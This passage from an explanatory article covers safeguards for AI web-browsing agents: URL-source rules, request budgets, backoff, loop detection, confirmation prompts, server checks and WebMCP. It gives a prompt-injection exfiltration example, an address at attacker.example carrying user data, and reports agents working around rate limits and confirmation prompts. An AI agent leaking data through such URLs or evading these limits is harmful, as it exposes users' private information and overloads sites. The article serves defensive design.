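Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a newer Chinese edition of the documentation, describes a loophole in this rule. By default, the output of the developer's own tools counts as a source of addresses, even when it repeats text that Claude wrote. If Claude runs a script that prints an invented address, or that fails with an error message quoting one, the fetch tool will open that address. Developers can close the loophole by listing either the tools to exclude as sources or the only tools to accept. The second option is safer because it also excludes any tool they add later.

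OpenAI uses a different test, which it described in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (January 2026). A crawler with no access to anybody's conversations or accounts builds an index of public web addresses. Before an agent automatically fetches an address, the software checks whether that exact address is in the index. If it is, the agent can open it. If not, the software either prompts the agent to try another site or warns the user before the address is opened.

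Both companies designed their rules to prevent data leaks. Prompt injection can make an agent open an address such as `attacker.example/collect?data=...`, with the user's private information after the equals sign. The attacker then reads it in the server's log. An address that a crawler found independently is unlikely to contain a particular user's private information.

The check also stops many invented addresses, which are usually missing from the index because the crawler had no page to find. An index lookup sends nothing to the site, whereas urlhealth tests an address by requesting it.

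The two rules stop different addresses:

| Address | Anthropic's rule | OpenAI's rule |
|---|---|---|
| A path the model invented | Refuses | Does not open automatically |
| A correct address the model remembers from training | Refuses | Opens if the index has it |
| A link to a page that went online an hour ago | Opens | Probably warns or suggests another site |
| A dead link on an old page | Opens | Opens if the index still has it |
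| An invented path that the agent's own script printed | Opens by default | Does not open automatically |

Neither rule guarantees that an address works. Deda found that other websites sometimes link to invented addresses, and an agent that reads such a link has a source for the address. A crawler may have recorded the same link. OpenAI's post does not explain how the company removes failed pages, so it is unclear whether its index would then include the dead address.

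OpenAI's rule is more likely to stop an agent from opening a legitimate page when the page is new or private, because the exact address may not be in the index. A crawler needs time to find a new press release, and it cannot reach a user's order history or a company's internal site. A search on the Larkhaven portal can also produce a legitimate address that nobody has used before, such as `/search?q=bus+ridership+2019`. The post does not report how often the rule stops an agent or how many of the stopped addresses were real. There seems to be an exception for addresses that the user types, which Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security blog, describes as safe for the rest of the session.

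A developer can also restrict an agent to a list of sites. This blocks requests to invented domains, but not to invented paths on a permitted site. OpenAI rejected such a list as its main protection because a trusted site may redirect visitors elsewhere, and a strict list produces so many warnings that people can learn to click through them.

A rule covers only the requests that are checked against it. Embrace The Red reports that an earlier OpenAI protection was missing from the company's Mac and iPhone apps. An agent's script creates a similar gap if it can reach the network directly, because it may open an invented address that the fetch tool would refuse.

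### Request budgets

An agent can still request thousands of addresses that each pass the check. A request budget limits how many requests the agent can send. A separate budget for each site protects a server better than a single total, since 100 requests to one small site burden its server more than one request to each of 100 sites.

Anthropic's fetch tool has a setting called `max_uses`, which limits the total number of fetches in one turn, meaning Claude's work between two messages from the user. Failed fetches count, so guessing addresses uses up the limit as fast as reading pages does. But there is no limit unless the developer sets one. Also, when a turn spans several requests to Anthropic's API, earlier fetches normally still count in later requests, but those that Claude ran from its own code do not.

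Because one action can start a script that sends thousands of requests, the software has to count the requests as they leave the computer.

A budget for each run doesn't limit the total across many runs. In the Department of Education case, a budget of 200 would have stopped a careless search for the codes before it was 1% complete. It would not have stopped a careful run, although about 1,080 careful runs could have produced the same total. A developer who runs many copies of an agent needs a budget that all of them share.

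The right budget is also hard to choose in advance. If Larkhaven had published no annual report, the agent would have needed 600 records to calculate the total, and a budget of 100 requests would have prevented it from doing what the user asked. The software can handle such cases by pausing at the limit and asking her whether to continue, preferably telling her how many requests the agent has sent and how many it expects to send.

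### When to retry, and how long to wait

An agent's response to a failed request should depend on the status code. After a 404, the software should remember the address and refuse to request it again during the task. After a 401 or 403, the agent should report the failure to the user. After a 429 or 503, it can try again, but only after waiting.

The server may state the wait in a "Retry-After" header, either as a number of seconds or as a date. The agent's software should treat this as a minimum. If the header is missing, it can use exponential backoff with a random delay. Counting the waits from $k = 0$, the length of each is

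$$w_k = \text{random}\bigl(0,\ \min(\text{cap},\ \text{base} \times 2^k)\bigr)$$

With a base of 1 second and a cap of 60 seconds, the upper limits of the first six waits are 1, 2, 4, 8, 16 and 32 seconds. Each wait is on average half its upper limit, so the six together average

$$\frac{1 + 2 + 4 + 8 + 16 + 32}{2} = 31.5 \text{ seconds}$$

and never exceed 63. The cap first matters at the seventh wait, where doubling would otherwise give 64 seconds.

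The random part of the wait keeps agents from retrying at the same time. If a server fails briefly while 1,000 agents are using it and each waits exactly one second, all 1,000 requests arrive together and may cause another failure. With random waits, the requests would be spread over 32 seconds by the sixth wait, or about 31 a second. Retry-After causes the same problem if a server gives every agent the same time, so the software should add a short random delay to it.

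Backoff helps much less when agents keep inventing addresses. In the earlier example with 1,000 agents on Larkhaven's portal, 30% of the addresses were invented and the software retried each one three times, for a total of 190 requests a second. Three random waits add an average of 3.5 seconds to each invented address. If an agent does nothing else in the meantime, the average time per address rises from 10 to 11.05 seconds, and the total falls only to

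$$\frac{1{,}000}{11.05} \times 1.9 \approx 172 \text{ requests a second}$$

This is still more than the 150 the server could handle in that example. Never retrying a 404 brings the total down to 100.

The software also has to enforce the wait. If it passes a 429 ("too many requests") error to the model and lets the model decide what to do, the model may look for another way in, as agents did in 44 of 72 runs in tests by Jha and colleagues. Pausing all requests to the site blocks some of these workarounds, but an agent can still look for a copy of the site elsewhere.

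### Detecting loops

Embrace The Red suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address more than once in a session, or storing each response for a few minutes and reusing it. Both are meant to stop an attacker from extracting secrets through repeated visits, and both would also reduce loops. But a strict ban would prevent an agent from returning to a page of search results or reloading after a brief failure. Reusing a stored response saves the server work, but the agent may keep looping.

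A loop detector can allow normal returns to a page by combining the address, a digest of the page's contents and the agent's action there into a triple. A digest is a short code calculated from a text. The same text always gives the same digest, and a changed text almost always gives a different one.

```
recent = empty list

before each action:
    triple = (address, digest(page text), action)
    seen = how often triple occurs in recent

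    if seen == 1:
        warn the model that it has done this before
    if seen >= 2:
        refuse the action and ask for a different one

    add triple to recent
    keep only the last 20 triples
```

The detector only warns the second time a triple occurs, because people sometimes reopen pages too, and refuses the action the third time. It can also catch an agent that alternates between two pages. With a window of 20 triples, it can refuse actions in cycles of up to 10 steps and warn about cycles of up to 20.

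Small changes on the page can defeat a loop detector that compares page digests. Suppose the Larkhaven portal shows a clock that updates every second, and the agent keeps clicking a menu that does not open. The digest changes with the clock, so the detector does not recognize the repeated clicks as a loop.

The developer could remove all digits from the text before calculating the digest. The clock would then no longer change the digest, but some lists would cause false alarms. For example, the portal might spread its numbered reports over many pages that all have the address `/reports`. The first page lists "Report 301" to "Report 310", and the next lists "Report 311" to "Report 320". Without digits, both pages contain the word "Report" ten times, so their digests match.

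| Situation | Digest of the full text | Digest without digits |
|---|---|---|
| Repeated clicks on a dead menu, with a clock on the page | No alarm | Refusal at the third click |
| Repeated clicks on "Next" in a list of numbered reports | No alarm | Refusal at the third click, although each page is new |

A developer can reduce both errors by computing the digest from only the main content, which leaves out the clock, or by making an exception for "Next". But each site needs slightly different fixes, and an agent visits sites its developer has never seen.

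The detector also misses guessed addresses, because each of the 24 possible variants of the Larkhaven path is a new action and no triple repeats. Address rules and budgets have to catch these guesses and the requests a script sends.

### Limiting what the agent can do in an account

The safeguards so far reduce the number of unwanted requests. Users can also reduce the harm from the remaining requests by giving the agent less access.

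A browser profile keeps its own cookies and saved passwords, so a user can create a separate one for the agent and log in only to the sites that a task needs. Looking up a public statistic would need no logins, but a separate profile does not reduce the number of requests the site receives. It also does not protect an account that the agent has to use. If the agent needs access to the user's email to find a refund, it can also send messages.

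Read-only access helps prevent side effects, but only if the service itself enforces it. Blocking every POST request in the browser would break many login forms and some search forms, and would still let through a badly designed "delete" link that uses GET. An email service, by contrast, can identify and refuse requests to send messages. Even with read-only access, the agent may reveal what it has read.

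An agent can also gain access that nobody gave it, as when one used a developer's leaked key to get Census data. Anthropic's fetch tool refuses addresses that appear to contain a key or password unless the credential appears in the user's message or the developer's standing instructions. This would block a leaked key placed in the address, but many services accept keys in a header instead, which a check on addresses would miss.

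### Asking the user first

Some actions that are hard to undo, such as paying for an order, have to remain possible. The software can hold these requests until the user confirms them. A confirmation prompt on the web page is not enough, because an agent can bypass it, as Google Web Accelerator did.

Deciding when an agent should ask for confirmation is difficult. A rule that covers every form would make it ask about harmless searches, but leaving the decision to the model is unreliable. The agent in the gym case asked before sending an email but not before cancelling a stranger's place. When ChatGPT uses functions that a website provides, OpenAI applies standard rules to purchases, messages, deletions and changes to permissions, according to Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP Connects AI Agents To Actions Inside Websites*. Cancelling someone else's booking might count as a deletion, but the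 software has to classify it as one for the rules to apply.

Users also stop reading the questions if there are too many. If an agent submits 40 forms and only two have lasting effects, asking every time produces 38 unnecessary questions. By the time an important one appears, the user may be approving them automatically. An "always allow" button avoids the repetition but removes the check. In the Muse sale, the seller had chosen it without realising that it covered his home address. A question showing the exact message, its recipient and any personal details would have given him a better chance to notice.

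A developer or user can also add a cautionary line to the prompt, such as "Do not guess addresses or take irreversible actions." OpenAI's confirmation policy is also a set of instructions to the model. It more than halved unintended outcomes for GPT-5.6 Sol but made little difference to GPT-6 Astra, which had few to begin with. A model can still ignore such instructions, as in the case of the mathematical proofs.

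A cautionary instruction also depends on the model recognising when it applies. A model that mistakes a plausible path for a real one will not apply an instruction against guessing. Software that checks the path against a list of known addresses doesn't depend on the model's judgement.

### Checks and limits on the server

A site's owner cannot rely on every agent's developer to use these safeguards. The most important protection on the server is a permission check on every endpoint that reads private data or changes anything. The endpoint looks up who owns the record and refuses the request if the account sending it has no right to that record. The gym's software made this check for bookings but not for cancellations.

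The check should be on the API endpoint because an agent may never open the page. Lù and colleagues warn that an agent with a powerful enough API key can bypass password prompts and two-factor authentication by calling the API directly.

Permission checks cannot stop an agent from making a mistake in its user's account, because the user is allowed to delete records or order twice. A shop can reduce double orders by putting a unique number in each order form and accepting each number only once. Clicking "Buy" twice on the same form then creates only one order, but if the agent loads and submits a new form, that form has a new number and the second order goes through.

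A site's owner can reduce the load from requests for missing pages. In the earlier example, storing 404 responses in the CDN cut the load on Larkhaven's own server from 127 to 37 requests a second. But if the CDN keeps a 404 response for five minutes and the city publishes a report at that address after one minute, visitors will get a 404 for another four minutes. The owner can also send a short message instead of a full page with images and menus, which helps even when each agent guesses a different address.

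A rate limit controls how fast one visitor can send requests. Suppose the portal allows 60 requests a minute. The Larkhaven script, at 20 requests a second, would reach the limit after three seconds and receive a 429 error. If it then obeyed the limit, its 1,801 requests would take about 30 minutes instead of a minute and a half. The server could easily handle that rate, but the total number of requests would be the same.

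The limit does less against many agents at once. A thousand agents that each open six pages a minute stay far below the limit of 60, yet together they send 100 requests a second. Everyone in an office may also share one IP address, so a limit for each address that is low enough to stop a crowd of agents may block a busy office too.

A robots.txt file is easy to publish, but it only works on software that follows it. Some agent software does, and Anthropic lists robots.txt among the reasons its fetch tool may refuse an address. A site owner could use the file to ask automated visitors to stay away from `/api/`, which would cover the endpoint in the Larkhaven example. The standard has no rule for request rate, so an owner can't use the file to allow ten requests a minute but not a thousand.

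### Signed requests

Rate limits and robots.txt would work better if a site could reliably tell which company's agent was visiting. To address this, the IETF's Web Bot Auth group is developing a way for automated clients to sign their requests cryptographically.

An agent's operator creates a pair of keys, keeps one private and publishes the other at a fixed address. The agent signs each request with the private key, and a header named "Signature-Agent" helps the site find the public key, which it uses to check the signature. Somebody without the private key cannot produce a valid signature, so the site can be much more confident about who operates the agent.

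The owner could then set one limit for all of an operator's agents, even if they used hundreds of IP addresses. She would also know whom to contact about a problem. But a valid signature does not make a request sensible, because an agent can also sign a request for an invented address.

The IETF's *Web Bot Auth* charter covers agents that visit websites on a user's behalf, but excludes HTTP APIs, the identity of the user, any common vocabulary for an agent's intentions and any system for rating agents' reputations. Calls to the school-statistics endpoint and the gym's booking API would probably fall outside it, as would the problem of recognising agents that do not sign their requests.

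The work is behind schedule. Under the charter, the technical specifications were due at the IETF's approval committee in April 2026, but the document history in IETF's *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (2026) shows that the group adopted the protocol draft only on September 1. The draft can still change, and sites cannot yet assume that most agents will follow it.

Signatures also make it easier to track who requests what. *Anonymous Bot Authentication* (Rescorla and Barnes, July 2026) describes an alternative that would let sites recognise wanted traffic and apply rate limits without tying each request to a particular sender. It is an individual proposal, not a standard. It would suit a site owner who cares more about volume than identity, but would give her less help in finding whoever caused a problem.

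### Interfaces made for agents

Many side effects begin when an agent cannot use a page designed for people. Lù and colleagues therefore proposed in 2025 that sites offer a separate interface for agents. It would give an agent only the information it needs and a defined set of actions, perhaps more than the site's API allows but fewer than a person has. Agents' tasks could be queued so that human visitors always have enough capacity. The team argued that site owners would spend less effort managing agents' traffic, but did not build a prototype.

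WebMCP, a proposal for browsers, applies part of this idea. A page registers some of its functions as tools, each with a name, a description and a definition of the inputs it accepts. The browser gives the agent this list. When the agent calls a tool, the browser runs the page's own code and returns the result.

The Larkhaven portal could offer a tool named `get_ridership` that takes a type of transport and a year. The agent would enter "bus" and "2019", and the page's code would find the figure. The agent would not have to guess a path, operate a menu or discover that the server's code for 2019 was 9. A tool can also stop before an irreversible step. For example, Shopify's checkout tool takes the customer to the checkout with her current cart but does not complete the purchase.

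WebMCP moved from a browser experiment into some live products during 2026. Shopify installed ten tools on every store that uses its standard Liquid templates. Cloudflare released a preview that adds tools to a site without changing the site's code. On August 25, OpenAI added WebMCP support to the browser in its ChatGPT desktop app.

Chrome and Edge are running origin trials of WebMCP, in which registered sites can use the feature before the browser's developers decide whether to adopt it. Chrome's trial runs through version 156, according to *WebMCP connects the Web to AI Assistants and Agents* (Nabors, 2026). Edge's ends on November 17, 2026, according to Microsoft's *WebMCP*.

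WebMCP is a draft from a community group of the W3C, which develops web standards. Nabors notes that it is neither a W3C standard nor on the track to become one, and that the group has removed or renamed several functions since March. Support from other browsers is uncertain. In August, Search Engine Journal reported that individual contributors had described Mozilla, which makes Firefox, as neutral and WebKit, the project behind Safari's engine, as opposed. On November 5, the unofficial guide *WebMCP* listed both positions as under discussion.

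No published figures show whether WebMCP reduces mistakes. Search Engine Journal found no error rates, counts of completed tasks or performance comparisons in the material from OpenAI, Shopify and Chrome. The claim that WebMCP is more reliable than clicking is plausible, because the agent has fewer steps to get wrong.

The tools also leave several causes of side effects in place. An agent must visit a site to find out which tools it offers (Chrome for Developers, 2026), so it may still guess the address of the first page. If no tool fits the task, ChatGPT may go back to clicking and typing. The tools run in the user's logged-in session, so a call with the wrong input can still change their account. Complex sites may need substantial new code, which gives their owners a reason to delay adding the tools.

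### The bus-ridership example again

Suppose the agent from the Larkhaven example now has most of these safeguards: a separate profile without logins, an address rule like Anthropic's, the loop detector and a budget of 100 requests for the portal. The portal limits each visitor to 60 requests a minute but offers no WebMCP tools. The address rule doesn't check requests made by the agent's scripts, but those requests count toward the budget.

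| Step in the original example | What the safeguards do |
|---|---|
| 1. Open the home page | Allow it, since a search result supplied the address |
| 2. Open an invented path | The address rule refuses it |
| 3. Try three variants | The address rule refuses all three |
| 4–6. Search and read two results | Allow all three steps |
| 7. Repeat the search and reopen the press release | The loop detector warns when the agent reopens the release |
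| 8. Notice the endpoint's address | Nothing to stop, because the agent sends no request |
| 9. Open the endpoint, then run a script | Allow the first request; the rate limit slows the script and the budget ends it |
| 10. Give the total without mentioning the requests | None of them requires a report |

The refusal in step 2 might already solve the problem, because the agent still has the home page open and could follow its "Publications" link to the annual report. It could also ignore the link and continue as before. Steps 4 to 7 would then use about eight requests and leave 92 for the endpoint.

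The budget would stop the script in the records for February 2017, because each month has 50 records. The portal would receive 100 requests instead of more than 1,800, but the user would not get the total she got without the budget unless the agent went back and found the report.

The first request to the endpoint in step 9 passed every safeguard. The agent had read the address on the page, had not opened it before and was well within its budget. The request changed nothing and used no login. It was still an unrequested call, because the agent could have reached the annual report in two clicks. A rule against calling any endpoint would stop it, but would also stop an agent from using a public API that the city had published for this purpose.
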